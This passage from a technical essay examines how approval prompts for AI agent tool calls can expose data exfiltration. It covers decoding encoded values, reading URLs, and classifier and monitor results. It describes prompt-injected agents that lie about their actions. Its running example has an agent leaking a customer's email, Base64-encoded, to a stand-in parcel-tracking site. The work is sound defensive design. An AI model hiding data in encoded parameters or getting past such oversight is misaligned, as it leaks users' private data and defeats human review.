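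The raw action also needs interpreting. A wallet can make a transaction readable with little work, but an agent's action may be a system command or a network request with encoded contents. Lioy, Ramunno and colleagues point out in *Motivations for a theoretical approach to WYSIWYS* that signers never see the bits they sign, only one possible representation of them, so interpretation is a problem for signatures too. This conflicts with Weng's view that classical signing had no such problem because the signed object was already meaningful. The problem is still harder for agents, whose actions take many more forms.

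Approving an agent's action on a phone gives only part of the protection of a hardware wallet, which shows the transaction on its own screen. In Kodathala and colleagues' system, a passkey (a cryptographic key stored on the phone) signs a value that includes the hash. The passkey displays nothing, so the reviewer has to trust the web page that shows the card.

### What the prototypes include

Weng's prototype is about 500 lines of Python and includes the analyser, the preview generator, and the hash check. The analyser gave no warning for 10% of the commands in a public catalogue of ways to abuse common tools. Weng assumed the other two parts, which are a trusted channel to the reviewer and a guarantee that the agent can act only through the mediator. The tests used a program that imitated a compromised agent, not a commercial product.

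Without that guarantee, the hash check is useless, because an agent with another way to send data can bypass it. An agent that can act only through MCP tools nearly meets it, because the harness's client sends every call. An agent that can run shell commands is much harder to contain, because any program it starts could open its own network connection unless the operating system prevents it.

Kodathala and colleagues also built the channel, using a gateway on a separate machine that sends approval cards to the user's phone. They used Tamarin, a tool for proving properties of security protocols, to prove that an action sent for approval runs only if the person approved that action or a grant that covers it. The proof assumes that the person decides from the trusted fields instead of the agent's explanation, that only the real user can register the first approval device, and that the page shows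 the correct card. Tamarin found an attack when they removed any of these assumptions. Designers can enforce secure registration but can't make people ignore an explanation on the screen.

### Should the agent's explanation appear at all?

Phone permissions offer the closest evidence on how stated reasons affect approval. When an iPhone app asks for access to data such as the user's contacts, the system's dialog can include the developer's explanation. In *The effect of developer-specified explanations for permission requests on smartphone user behavior*, Tan, Nguyen and colleagues (2014) tested these explanations by showing people screenshots of requests with and without a reason, along with a request from an invented party-planning app that gave one of 14 reasons.

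Xu reports in *Ubiquitous and Mobile Computing CS 528*, a set of lecture slides about the experiment, that the 568 participants in the comparison approved 74% of requests with a reason and 66% of those without, a statistically significant difference. Approval rates did not differ significantly among the 14 reasons shown.

Later work suggests that the wording can matter. CISPA, a German research centre for information security, reports on a study by its researcher Elbitar in which people were more likely to approve requests that gave specific reasons than vague ones. Elbitar attributes this to people feeling better informed and more in control when they understand why an app requests access. Those feelings are a problem if the reason is false, because the person is no better protected than before.

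A larger experiment found that giving a reason had no measurable effect. Berke and Johnson (2026), in *Approximate vs Precise*, showed location requests from a wallpaper app, a local news app and a ride-share app to 2,579 Android users in the US. Each request came with an informative reason, an uninformative reason, a reason that mentioned advertising, or no reason. The wallpaper app had no need for the user's location, yet most people allowed it. The share who refused was 40.9% without a reason and between 42.1% and 43.9% with one. Only 32% of participants could later identify the last reason they had seen, and the reasons had no measurable effect on those people either.

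The two experiments were 12 years apart and covered different phone systems and kinds of data, so it is hard to say why only the older one found an effect. Both used hypothetical requests, and neither provides evidence that reasons help people tell a justified request from an unjustified one, which a reviewer has to do. If an agent's explanation makes people more willing to approve everything, it lowers the false alarm rate but raises the miss rate.

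Many people also don't know who wrote the explanation in a permission prompt. In *Can Systems Explain Permissions Better?*, Shen, Wei and colleagues (2021) found that 54.7% of the iPhone users they asked did not know that it came from the app's developer. Most of those users thought the system had written it. In interviews, some people said the explanations looked too consistent across apps to be the developers' work. People could similarly mistake an agent's explanation inside a harness's prompt for the harness's own. Shen and colleagues suggest naming the source in the dialog.

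They also tested information that the system itself could provide. Of the people who had first allowed a request, 17% to 46% changed their answer after an unfavourable message about the app's background access to data, depending on the phone and the scenario. Asking people again straight after a warning probably exaggerates the effect, but the result suggests that people respond to relevant facts in a prompt.

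The argument for including the agent's explanation is that reviewers need to know why it is proposing an action. The practitioners Salerno and colleagues studied cared whether an action matched what they had wanted and whether they could undo it. A destination and a list of data don't settle that. The harness can supply some context without the agent's help by showing the user's original request and a log of earlier steps, as Hossain and colleagues did. Only the agent can give its reason for choosing this site, though, and that reason may reveal a mistake.

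Weng compromises by showing the agent's explanation but labeling it as untrusted. Kodathala and colleagues do the same, and also keep it collapsed until the reviewer opens it. They tested the design on 609 pairs of ordinary tasks and injected attacks, with the agent lying about what it was doing. A simulated reviewer who believed any explanation on display let 54% of the attacks through, the same as with a card written entirely by the agent. Removing the explanation reduced this to 5%. The 15 language models, by contrast, behaved almost identically with and without the explanation.

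Neither project tested the label on people. The phone studies suggest that many reviewers will ignore the explanation and that some will trust it too much, so the preview should make sense without it. For the parcel lookup, the prompt might look like this:

```
The agent wants to open a web page.

Site:          track.parcel-status.example
Data sent:     id = mara@example.org
Your request:  Summarise this complaint and check on the parcel.

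> Agent's explanation (written by the agent, not verified)

Allow        Deny
```

The harness takes the site and the data from the stored call, and the request from the user's own message. If the reviewer opens the agent's explanation, it might read "Look up the parcel by its tracking number". The line above it shows that the "tracking number" is an email address, so an explanation that would be reassuring alone gives the reviewer a reason to stop. If the reviewer allows the call anyway, the approval covers only the full URL, including the original encoded string, and the agent can't use the approval to send anything else.

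## Decoding what the call carries

A preview can show "id = mara@example.org" only if the harness decodes the string in the URL. The harness has to do this without the agent's help, because a manipulated agent may have encoded the data to hide it. It also has to detect when decoding has failed, since a wrong result presented as certain could mislead the reviewer more than the raw string would.

### The decoding steps

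A harness can work through a call in this order:

1. Split the call into named parameters. An MCP server supplies an input schema for each tool, which is a machine-readable list of its parameters and their types. A web address needs a further split into the site, the path and the named values after the question mark.
2. Undo percent-encoding, which writes special characters in web addresses as a percent sign and two hexadecimal digits. For example, "%40" becomes "@".
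3. Try to reverse Base64, hexadecimal (two characters from 0–9 and a–f for each byte) and common compression formats. If one works, try them all again on the result, up to a fixed number of rounds.
4. Accept the final result if it is readable text or matches data the agent has read. Otherwise, keep the original.
5. Make invisible and look-alike characters visible.
6. If the call runs a script, open the script and analyse it too.
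7. Mark anything left over as uninspectable.

A preview can miss data if it shows only the fields listed in a tool's schema. Under the Model Context Protocol (MCP) specification, a schema that declares only "an object" accepts any fields, so the preview has to include unlisted ones too. Some data also travels outside the parameters. A server can reply that it needs more input, and the client then repeats the call with the user's answers attached. The preview of the repeated call should include those answers, such as the GitHub username in one MCP example.

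The limit on rounds stops a value built to keep the harness decoding forever. Decompression also needs a size limit, because a small file can expand into an enormous one. A value that reaches either limit is uninspectable. Speed is not otherwise a problem. Weng's analyser, which removes layers of encoding from system commands in a similar way, averaged 0.056 milliseconds per command. The analyser's preview shows the number of layers removed and the original command next to the decoded one.

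The harness needs the test in step 4 because many ordinary words are also valid Base64. The word "data" decodes to three bytes that don't form valid text. Short values sometimes decode to readable text by chance. A random byte has a 95 in 256 chance of being a printable character in ASCII, the basic set of English letters, digits and punctuation. Three random bytes are all printable about 5% of the time, but 16 are all printable only about once in eight million. The harness can therefore accept a long readable result, but should show a short one beside the original unless it also matches something the agent has read.

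Text can also contain characters that take up no space, change the direction of surrounding text or look identical to other characters. The harness can replace each invisible character with a visible mark, such as its number in Unicode, the standard catalogue of characters. It has to do this after decoding, because the decoded text may contain invisible characters too.

MCP recommends that tool names use only unaccented Latin letters, digits and three punctuation marks, so a harness can treat any other character in a name as suspicious. It can't do the same for parameter values, because a customer's name may be in any alphabet, and Persian spelling and some emoji depend on invisible characters. Mixed alphabets within one word are a better reason for a warning than non-Latin text alone.

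Scripts need their own step because a command like "python3 deploy.py" doesn't show what the file does. Players in scalex.dev's game missed just over half of the threats inside scripts with familiar names. Weng's analyser reads the file and clears it only if it stays within a limited set of operations. If the script uses the network, starts other programs, builds new code as it runs or writes outside the agent's workspace, the analyser either reports the danger or marks the script uninspectable. It also flags the command if it can't find the file.

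To avoid repeated prompts, the analyser checks a file when the agent writes it and reuses the verdict when the agent runs it. It treats running a downloaded file as running code from the network. The weak point is software that the agent builds on the machine, because the analyser trusts a build tool's output even though the build may have included outside code that nobody checked.

### The parcel value by hand

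Base64 uses 64 characters, each standing for a number from 0 to 63. Capital letters stand for 0 to 25, lowercase letters for 26 to 51, digits for 52 to 61, "+" for 62 and "/" for 63. Each character encodes six bits and a byte has eight, so four characters hold exactly three bytes.

The value in the parcel lookup is "bWFyYUBleGFtcGxlLm9yZw==". Its first four characters, "bWFy", decode like this:

1. Look up the numbers: b = 27, W = 22, F = 5, y = 50.
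2. Write each in six bits: 011011 010110 000101 110010.
3. Regroup the same 24 bits in eights: 01101101 01100001 01110010.
4. Read those as numbers: 109, 97 and 114, the character codes for "m", "a" and "r".

The other groups work the same way.

| Base64 | Six-bit numbers | Bytes | Text |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| bWFy | 27, 22, 5, 50 | 109, 97, 114 | mar |
| YUBl | 24, 20, 1, 37 | 97, 64, 101 | a@e |
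| eGFt | 30, 6, 5, 45 | 120, 97, 109 | xam |
| cGxl | 28, 6, 49, 37 | 112, 108, 101 | ple |
| Lm9y | 11, 38, 61, 50 | 46, 111, 114 | .or |
| Zw== | 25, 48 | 103 | g |

In the last group, two characters supply 12 bits, but the letter "g" needs only eight, so the decoder discards the other four, which are zeros. The equals signs pad the group to four characters and carry no data. Many systems omit them, and web addresses often use "-" and "_" in place of "+" and "/", so the harness should accept these variants.

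The result is 16 readable characters that also appear in the customer's complaint, so it passes both tests in step 4. The preview should still add "decoded from Base64", because there is little reason to encode an email address in an ordinary parcel lookup.

### Values that resist decoding

A harness can't read encrypted data without the key, and a genuine random identifier has no message to find. The two can look exactly alike. The harness can still work out how much a value could hold. If a string has n characters and each can be any of k symbols, there are kⁿ possible strings. One string can therefore pick out one of at most kⁿ messages, which gives a capacity in bits of:

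log₂(kⁿ) = n · log₂(k)

Without its equals signs, the parcel value has 22 characters. Each is one of 64 possible characters, which is 6 bits, so the value can hold 22 × 6 = 132 bits. That is enough for the 16 bytes (128 bits) of mara@example.org in ASCII.

| Value | Capacity | Whole bytes |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The "a1b2c3" in MCP's sample basket identifier (6 small letters or digits) | 31 bits | 3 |
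| A 12-digit parcel number | 40 bits | 4 |
| A random UUID, a common type of identifier (32 hexadecimal digits, with 6 bits fixed) | 122 bits | 15 |
| 22 Base64 characters | 132 bits | 16 |

The harness may have to infer the alphabet from one example. If "a1b2c3" is hexadecimal, its capacity is 24 bits instead of 31. When in doubt, the harness should assume the larger alphabet. Even a value with a small capacity can leak a secret. A four-digit PIN needs only 14 bits, so the short basket identifier has room for two.

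When decoding fails, the preview can fall back on a statement about capacity:

```
Data sent:   id = q7Xk2mVb9TzR4wLs8NcHfA
             Could not decode. This field could hold a short
             secret (up to 16 bytes).
```

This is accurate, but it would be just as accurate for many harmless calls, such as those that pass a basket identifier back to a shop. For servers that don't check who is calling, MCP recommends making these identifiers hard to guess, for example with random UUIDs. A shop that followed this advice could trigger the warning every time the agent added an item to a basket, and the user would soon stop reading it.

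A threshold would remove some of these false alarms. If the harness warned only above 64 bits, the short basket identifier would pass, but so would a PIN, and a UUID would still trigger the warning. A better rule is to skip the warning when a value goes back unchanged to the server that issued it, because that server already has the value. The harness has to identify the server from its own connection records, since MCP doesn't guarantee that the names servers report are unique. The parcel value would still trigger a warning, because the tracking site never issued it.

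### What happened when Weng tested a decoder

Weng ran the analyser on two public collections of system commands. The first, GTFOBins, catalogues ways to abuse ordinary programs, for example to read protected files or move data off a machine. Weng turned it into 1,330 commands covering 478 programs. The second, tldr-pages, contains 28,798 examples of normal use for 6,503 tools.

| Result | Catalogued abuses | Normal commands |
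| --- | --- | --- |
| Prompted, for any reason | 90.0% | 95.9% |
| Marked uninspectable | 59.5% | 87.0% |
| Passed without a prompt | 10.0% | 4.1% |

The analyser flagged 1,197 abuses and gave a specific danger for 405 of them. It marked the other 792 uninspectable. That mark was of almost no use to a reviewer in these tests, because normal commands received it more often than abuses did.

Both results depend heavily on a trust list, which names the programs the analyser may let through if it finds nothing dangerous. The analyser marks a command that uses any other program as uninspectable by default. This rule alone accounts for the mark on 83.4% of the normal commands. All 133 abuses that passed without a prompt used programs on the list.

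Removing a program from the list would catch the abuses that run through it, but the analyser would also flag the program's normal uses. Adding a program has the opposite effect. Weng concludes that a tool that only examines commands before they run can be tuned to miss fewer abuses or to raise fewer false alarms, but not both.

Better analysis can still make the trade-off less severe. An earlier version of the analyser let 15.0% of the abuses through. Weng reduced this to 10.0% by detecting more writes outside the workspace, checking every program for attempts to read credentials and examining commands nested inside other commands. Many of the remaining 133 also have specific causes:

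- 85 wrote to temporary folders, which the analyser doesn't count as outside the workspace.
- 19 wrote files inside the workspace that would become dangerous only when a later command used them.
- 8 were harmless basics, such as creating a folder.
- 21 were genuine gaps in the analysis.

The figure for normal commands probably overstates how often a developer would see a prompt. The collection covers thousands of tools that most people never use, while a developer runs the same few dozen all day and could add those to the list. Some of the prompts were also appropriate, since normal commands include ones that delete files and overwrite disks.

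Weng also wrote 22 attacks to test the analyser, including encoded commands and harmful scripts. The analyser explained 17, marked five uninspectable and let none through. But Weng warns against relying on this result, because the same person designed both the attacks and the defence. An earlier version had also scored perfectly on its own test set while missing common abuses.

A shell command is a small program, so it is harder to parse than an MCP call with named parameters. A decoder for MCP calls might leave fewer values unexplained, but its designers would still have to decide which tools to trust. They could also make the mark more useful by separating its two meanings. It can mean that the tool is not on the user's trusted list, which is a gap in the settings, or that a value could not be decoded, which is something unusual in the call itself.

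### Clear signing

Cryptocurrency users have a similar problem. On Ethereum, a blockchain that runs programs called smart contracts, a transaction contains bytes that specify which function a contract should run and with what values. When a wallet can't interpret those bytes, it shows its owner a long hexadecimal string to approve, a practice known as blind signing. In clear signing, the wallet shows readable fields instead.

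In an early step, *EIP 712* by Bloemen, Logvinov and Evans set a standard for messages that people sign outside a transaction. It encodes the data along with its structure, so a wallet can list named fields such as "from", "to" and "contents". The signature also covers a value specific to the application, so another application can't reuse the signature.

Be'ery and RoiV argued in *ERC-6384* (2023) that average users still could not understand these messages even when the fields were named. Trail of Bits' *Implement EIP-7730 today* (2025) gives the example of the $1.5 billion theft from the cryptocurrency exchange Bybit. The attackers changed the destination address and switched an "operation" field from 0 to 1, which let their own code run. A wallet could display both fields correctly, but few people would know what the 1 meant.

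The newer standard, *ERC-7730* (Castillo, Rein and colleagues, 2024), adds a published file called a descriptor. It lists the contracts it applies to and gives each function a plain statement of purpose, with a label and display format for each value. In Trail of Bits' example, a wallet turns "amountIn: 500000000000000000" and several other fields into "Swap 0.5 ETH for minimum 800 USDC".

Sourcify's *Introduction to ERC-7730* explains that a contract's standard interface description can identify an amount as a whole number without giving the currency or the position of the decimal point. The descriptor supplies these missing details. Ledger, a hardware wallet maker, points out that the descriptor changes only the display, and the wallet still signs the original transaction.

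Castillo and colleagues also cover cases where decoding fails. If the descriptor doesn't include a function, the wallet should show something like "Unknown function" with the raw values. If the wallet can't decrypt a value, it should show a clear placeholder, preferably with at least part of the raw value. When one call contains another, the wallet looks for a second descriptor, and if it finds none, it may show a hash of the inner call.

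An attacker can write a misleading descriptor, so wallets need a way to decide which ones to trust. Sourcify stresses that a descriptor's inclusion in the public registry does not mean it is safe. A companion proposal, *ERC-8176*, lets auditors and wallet makers sign statements that a descriptor is correct. *Clear Signing* (Bruikman, 2026) announced the launch of the wider system in May 2026, with each wallet deciding whose reviews to accept.

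In the standard's discussion thread, *EIP-7730*, one participant argues that wallets should distinguish a descriptor removed as malicious from one that never existed. A user should treat the first as a warning, while the second may only mean that the contract is new.

### What tool schemas would need

MCP's input schemas resemble Ethereum's interface descriptions more than its descriptors. In the sample weather tool, the "location" parameter is a string described as "City name or zip code". That description could help a reviewer notice an email address in the field, but the schema would accept the address because it is also a string.

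MCP also has annotations, optional hints about whether a tool changes anything, whether the change is destructive, whether repeating the call is safe and whether the tool deals with outside parties. They describe the tool in general, not the values in one call. In a March 2026 post, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported that no MCP client showed them in approval prompts.

An equivalent of clear signing for tool calls would need at least four things.

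- Formats that the harness can check. If a parcel tool required exactly 12 digits, the harness could reject an email address in any encoding, and the field's capacity would drop from 132 bits to 40. JSON Schema, the language MCP uses for input schemas, can already express such rules.
- A link to one specific tool. An ERC-7730 descriptor applies to contracts at listed addresses. MCP servers can change their tools over time, so a descriptor would have to identify both the server and the exact version of the tool's definition.
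- Review by someone other than the server's operator. An untrusted server can lie in its annotations, and it could lie in a descriptor too.
- Limits on hiding fields. ERC-7730 lets a descriptor's author mark a field as never shown. In a tool call the agent fills in the fields, so data could leave through a hidden one even if the tool's author is honest. The harness should show any field with room for more than a few bits.

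Review would also be harder than on Ethereum, where an auditor can compare a descriptor with a contract's published code. An auditor usually can't see the code running on a remote MCP server. The operator could change how that code handles the data without changing the tool's definition, so a descriptor can show what the server will receive but not what happens to the data afterward.

Even a perfect descriptor would not explain the original parcel lookup, because the agent used a general tool for fetching web pages and nobody can describe what "id" means on every website. Descriptors suit narrow tools, such as one that accepts a parcel number and returns a delivery date. For web browsing and shell commands, the harness has to rely on decoding, which is a reason to give agents narrow tools where they exist.

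Adoption may be slow because many MCP servers don't provide even the existing annotations. Model Context Protocol suggests testing new metadata in a field reserved for custom information before proposing it as a standard, but ready-made clients would ignore anything they didn't recognise.

An independent proposal, *MCP For Humans*, would add previews and a standard dry run, which reports what a call would do without doing it. Dry runs could help with deletions or purchases, but they would not prevent exfiltration if the server ran them, because the server would already have the data.

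### Long values

An email body or uploaded file can fill several screens, and decoding can turn a short compressed string into pages of text. Castillo and colleagues warn that very long values can push critical information off the screen. They allow wallets to shorten long descriptions if users can expand them.

The preview should start with the destination and any private data the harness has found. Each field should have a maximum height, so that a long one can't push the others out of sight. The harness can safely collapse the original form of a value it has decoded and the unremarkable parts of a long text. It should keep showing any private data it has recognised, a notice for every value it can't inspect, and the name of every field that isn't in the schema.

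The usual way to shorten an identifier is to show its first and last few characters, which works only if those characters differ between values. Castillo and colleagues advise wallets that shorten references to encrypted values to leave out parts with a fixed structure, because they don't help users tell the values apart. A greeting at the start of an email likewise reveals little about the rest, so an extract from around the private data is more useful.

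Three dots are a poor sign that text is missing, because they could be part of the text and don't indicate how much is gone. The harness should add its own line, outside the area that shows the value, with the amount hidden and what it contains:

```
The agent wants to send an email.

To:          help@parcel-status.example
Contains:    1 customer email address (mara@example.org)
Subject:     Delivery query
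Body:        "Hello, I am writing about a parcel that ..."

[Harness: 1,912 more characters folded. All text checked.]
> Show full text
```

The harness has to search the full text before shortening it, or the "Contains" line could miss something in the folded part. If the search stops at a size limit, the notice should show how much was left unchecked, for example "40,000 characters not checked". For an attachment, the preview can give the file's name and size and a count of what the harness found, such as "214 customer email addresses", so that a reviewer can act on the count without opening the file.

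## Showing where the data is going

Decoding the parcel lookup shows that the call sends mara@example.org. Whether that is a leak depends on who receives it, and so far the preview gives only a web address, track.parcel-status.example. For about twenty years, researchers have studied how people read web addresses, mostly to understand phishing, in which a fake site imitates a real one to collect passwords and often differs visibly only in its address.

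### The parts of a web address

A web address, or URL, has several parts, and they differ in how much a reviewer can learn from them.

| Part | In the parcel lookup | What a reviewer can learn from it |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Scheme | https | The connection is encrypted, which a dishonest site can offer too |
| Subdomain | track | Little, because the domain's owner can choose any word |
| Registrable domain | parcel-status.example | Which registered name controls the site |
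| Path | /lookup | Little, because the site's owner chooses this as well |
| Query | id=bWFyYUBleGFtcGxlLm9yZw== | What the agent is sending, once the harness decodes it |

*The Web's Identity Crisis* (Thompson, Shelton and colleagues, 2019) defines the registrable domain as the suffix under which people can register names, plus the one label before it. In accounts.google.co.uk, the suffix is "co.uk" and the registrable domain is google.co.uk. An organisation that controls a registrable domain can typically control every subdomain and path within it. The operator of the parcel site could therefore choose the words "track" and "lookup", and anyone could have registered a name containing "parcel".

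The most important part of a URL is in the middle, because subdomains run from specific to general, like the lines of a postal address, and the path after them runs the other way. Tim Berners-Lee, who invented the web, has said he regrets the clumsy syntax and would have preferred a single order, starting with the domain suffix.

A harness can reliably find the registrable domain with the Public Suffix List, a catalogue of suffixes that browsers also use. Counting dots is unreliable because some suffixes, such as "com", have one label and others, such as "co.uk", have two.

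### What people think an address means

For *Why Phishing Works*, Dhamija, Tygar and Hearst (2006) asked 22 people to say which of 19 websites were fake. Participants knew that some were, yet they judged only 11.6 correctly on average. Five of them never looked at the address bar, and they got the five lowest scores. The best fake, a copy of a bank's website with an address very close to the real one, fooled 20 participants, including a customer of the bank who had expert knowledge of security.

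Participants also distrusted genuine sites, with 77% judging a stockbroker's real mobile site fake and 50% judging a bank's real login page fake. Both used another company's domain. Reviewers of tool calls could easily make the same mistake, because a shop may well use an outside company's site to track its parcels.

In *What is this URL's Destination?*, Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020) showed 1,929 people 23 URLs, without any fake pages, and asked where each would lead. Twelve combined an organisation's name with the word "profile" or "mobile". Six of these had the organisation's name in the domain, as in profile.facebook.com, which leads to Facebook, and six had it in the subdomain, as in facebook.profile.com, which leads to a site controlled by whoever owns profile.com.

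On average, participants answered 5.2 of the first six correctly and 1.2 of the second six. Their total of 6.4 out of 12 was barely better than the 6 they would have scored by always picking the organisation's name, which 32.2% of them did. Another 8.3% got all twelve right. Experience with technology helped only a little. When the name was in the subdomain, the heaviest technology users were right 25.4% of the time, compared with 15.9% for the group with the least coding experience.

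Most people don't realise that they have trouble telling which site a URL leads to. In *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators* (2020), Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues asked 94 people to identify the site behind each of up to 19 URLs. They succeeded with 93% of ordinary URLs but only 40% of those the researchers had altered to be misleading. Yet 91 of the 94 said it was mostly or very true that they knew how to read a URL. When asked how they decide whether a link is safe, 27 people said they check for "https", which was the most common answer.

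Most of these participants (69) mainly looked for the name of an organisation, while 15 looked for the domain name. Those who looked for the domain name did better, but their median score was only 62.5%, compared with 55.5% for those who looked for an organisation's name.

Albakry and Reynolds's results apply more directly to approval prompts than the older experiment's do, because a reviewer also sees a URL with no web page around it. But the reviewer's task is harder in one respect, because the agent chose the site and the reviewer may not know which organisation to expect. Someone checking for phishing does know, and can compare the address with the organisation's name. A reviewer who correctly reads "parcel-status.example" still doesn't know whose site it is.

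### Making the domain stand out

Browser makers draw attention to the domain, usually by showing it darker than the rest of the URL. *Does Domain Highlighting Help People Identify Phishing Sites?* (Lin, Greenberg and colleagues, 2011) tested this with 22 people and 16 web pages, half of them fake. Participants first rated 57% of the fake pages as safe. When the researchers told them to look at the address bar and rate the pages again, this fell to 44%.

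*Is Domain Highlighting Actually Helpful in Identifying Phishing Web Pages?* criticizes the earlier research because the browser highlighted the domain in both rounds, so the improvement may have come entirely from the instruction. In *Ineffectiveness of Domain Highlighting*, Xiong, Yang and colleagues (2016) reported a larger online test in which 320 people judged six pages. They concluded that highlighting did not work.

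Some people in Lin's experiment noticed a problem and trusted the page anyway. One found the highlighted part of a fake bank's address strange but rated the page as trustworthy because "banks are secure".

Reynolds and colleagues had slightly better results. They gave 40 of their participants the aids browsers offer, such as highlighting the domain name and decoding escaped characters. This group identified 61.1% of the URLs, compared with 56.1% for the others, a small but statistically significant difference.

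Thompson and colleagues, who all worked at Google, tested bolder designs. They showed more than 1,000 people a copy of Google's login page at an address belonging to TinyURL, a link-shortening service. Each person saw one of seven versions of the address bar. Across all seven, 85% of people said the site was Google and 13% identified it correctly. Among people who saw the version with only the registrable domain, 13% expressed a general doubt about the site's safety, compared with 2% for the standard design. However, how comfortable people felt about logging in did not differ significantly between the designs.

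Google then tried the same idea on real users, announcing the trial in Chromium Blog's *Helping people spot the spoofs* (2020). According to 9to5Google (2020), one reason was research in which a misleading brand name in a URL's path fooled more than 60% of people. PortSwigger's *Grand omnibox experiment failed to hit the mark* reports that the trial began with Chrome 86 and covered a small percentage of users. The trial ended in June 2021. In Chromium's *Delete simplified domain experiment*, the developers wrote that the change "didn't move relevant security metrics", but they gave no figures.

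Displaying the owner's legal name did not help much either. Chrome used to show a company's legal name beside the URL if its site had an Extended Validation certificate, which requires extra checks on the company's identity. In an experiment with millions of users, Thompson and colleagues found that removing the name made little difference to most of what people did on those sites. The legal name can also be unfamiliar. For example, the certificate for mint.com, a personal finance site, named "Intuit Inc."

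These findings make it unlikely that bolding the domain would fix an approval prompt. A destination line may still be useful, because an approval prompt interrupts people and contains only a few lines, whereas an address bar sits at the edge of a page they are busy using.

### Designs that helped people check a link

The nearest thing to an approval prompt in this research is a box that shows a URL again and asks the user to confirm it. *URL Inspection Tasks* (2025) compares that design with three others. The figures are the share of phishing emails that succeeded:

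| What happened after a click | Phishing success |
| --- | --- |
| No extra step | 74% |
| The URL appeared again and the user confirmed | 57% |
| The user dragged parts of the URL back into place | 61% |
| The user completed a task that required inspecting the URL | 35% |

Showing the address and asking for confirmation helped, but more than half the attacks still succeeded. Dragging the pieces into place took more effort and worked no better, probably because people could finish the puzzle without considering whether they wanted to visit the site. The inspection tasks worked much better. They would be too slow for every tool call, but a harness might require one only the first time an agent sends private data to an unknown party, though this use is untested.

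The position of a warning matters too. Petelka, Zou and Schaub (2019), in *Put Your Warning Where Your Link Is*, tested placing email warnings next to the suspicious link, showing them when the mouse hovered over it, and forcing people to pay attention to them. *Anti-Phishing Warnings in Email Inboxes*, a summary of this line of work, reports that warnings near the link worked better than warnings at the top of the email or on a full page shown after the click.

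According to the summary, restricting the link, for example by briefly delaying clicks, can also make a warning more effective. *Restricting the Link*, by Petelka, Berens and colleagues, describes an alternative to a delay, in which the user can continue only by clicking the uncovered address inside the warning. The 2019 experiment did not put warnings on harmless links, so it could not measure false alarms.

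An approval prompt should put any warning about the destination directly under the destination. A banner at the top, such as "This action may be risky," leaves the reviewer to work out which line it refers to.

A different approach is to give people facts they couldn't get from the URL. Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea (2021), in *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible*, point out that even security experts struggle to judge a link without tools and additional information, such as the domain's age. They explain such features in terms ordinary users can understand. An earlier project, Althobaiti, Vaniea and Zheng's *Faheem*, used a Slack chat bot to explain URLs.

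Reynolds and colleagues note that people who had used such a tool did worse once they no longer had it. This is disappointing for training but matters less for a harness, which can show the explanation in every permission prompt. The prompt could include a line such as "This site's name is 9 days old". A new domain is only weak evidence of a problem, since every honest business starts with one, and an old domain offers little reassurance if thousands of strangers can publish on it.

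### When the domain is the wrong unit

Albakry and colleagues argue that helping people read URLs is not enough, because they need to know who controls the content a URL leads to. Microsoft owns windows.net and Google owns googleusercontent.com, but customers of both companies can host their own content there. A reviewer who correctly identifies the domain's owner would still be wrong about who controls the page.

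A domain name often doesn't show who will receive the data, because agents do much of their work through services with many customers. An upload to the user's own folder and an upload to a stranger's may go to the same domain. The preview needs to identify the destination account and show who will be able to see the data.

| Action | What the domain identifies | What the preview should add |
| --- | --- | --- |
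| Send an email | The mail provider | Every recipient's full address, including copies, and which ones are outside the user's organisation |
| Push code | The code-hosting service | The owner, the repository and whether the public can read it |
| Post in a chat | The chat service | The workspace and channel, the number of members and any outside guests |
| Share a document | The storage service | The people who will gain access, or "anyone with the link" |
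| Upload to cloud storage | The cloud provider | The account that owns the storage and whether its contents are public |

Some commands don't include the address they send data to. In the Git command "git push origin main", which uploads code, "origin" is a nickname for an address stored in a settings file on the developer's machine. A preview that only repeats the command doesn't show where the code will go. The harness should look up the current address, show it, and make sure the push goes there even if the settings change before the command runs.

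The harness should show the address next to the name of any person or group. An address book may show "Accounts team" for a mailing list with 200 members, some of them outside the company, so the harness should also show the number of members if it can find out. If it can't, "number of recipients unknown" is more useful than the name alone.

Some hosting services give each customer a subdomain, so a preview that trimmed the subdomain would hide which customer receives the data. The Public Suffix List covers many of these services by treating the host's domain as a suffix, which makes the customer's subdomain part of the registrable domain. Services that identify customers in the path, as code hosts usually do, need their own rule in the harness.

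### Public, private or trusted

In August 2026, Anthropic described how Claude Code's auto mode checks where data is going. Before the agent pushes code or opens a pull request (a proposal to merge changes into a repository), a classifier checks whether the destination is public, private or trusted. It also has separate rules for where secrets, such as passwords, and other information that may be confidential can go.

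Anthropic puts data exfiltration in a category that the classifier should never approve. A user who wants to take such an action has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. Organisations can add other actions to the category.

The evidence for the visibility check comes from Apollo Research's tests. After the first round of attacks, Anthropic improved the classifier mainly by giving it more context, including whether the repository was public or private, the state of its code, and the data-handling rules. On a new set of attacks, the improved classifier caught about half of those the earlier version would have missed, and missed about 2% of those the earlier version would have caught. Anthropic made these changes together, so the result does not show how much the visibility check contributed.

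The check also informs a classifier, not a person. Anthropic reports no test in which reviewers saw a repository's visibility in a prompt. The closest evidence is from Yan's simulation, where most people refused the public travel post.

A preview of a push could present the same facts like this:

```
The agent wants to push code.

Sends to:    code-host.example / mara-demos / shop-site
             PUBLIC: anyone on the internet can read this.
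Data sent:   3 commits, 12 files

Allow        Deny
```

The prompt needs to show both the repository's owner and its visibility. A stranger can read anything sent to their own private repository, so the word "private" alone could reassure a reviewer who ought to be worried. A "trusted" label is safer if it comes from a list that the user or the organisation keeps than if it relies on the repository's name, which an agent or an outsider can choose.

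The harness can usually check whether a repository is public or private by querying the hosting service. If the query fails, the preview should show "visibility unknown" rather than label the repository private. Even a correct result can become outdated, because the owner of a private repository can make it public later, usually with its whole history.

### Redirects

A site can respond to a request by redirecting the harness to a different address. Most redirects are harmless. In *Shim Shimmeny*, Li (2020) describes how Facebook, Twitter, Microsoft and Google have rewritten links on their sites for over a decade, partly for security, so that a click goes through an intermediate address first. Link-shortening services also use redirects.

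People seem to be wary of short links. Albakry's participants gave them a median safety rating of 2 out of 5, compared with 4 for the URLs with a subdomain. But an ordinary-looking URL can redirect too, and Albakry and colleagues note that even a computer can't tell whether it does without visiting it.

For a browser that is a nuisance, but for a harness trying to prevent a leak it is a more serious problem. Visiting the first address would already send any private data in the URL, so the harness can't trace the route first and ask for approval afterwards. It can take the route one step at a time:

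1. Show the address in the call and ask about that destination.
2. If the reviewer allows it, send the request with automatic redirects switched off.
3. If the reply is a redirect, compare the new destination with the approved one, by account where the service has accounts and otherwise by registrable domain.
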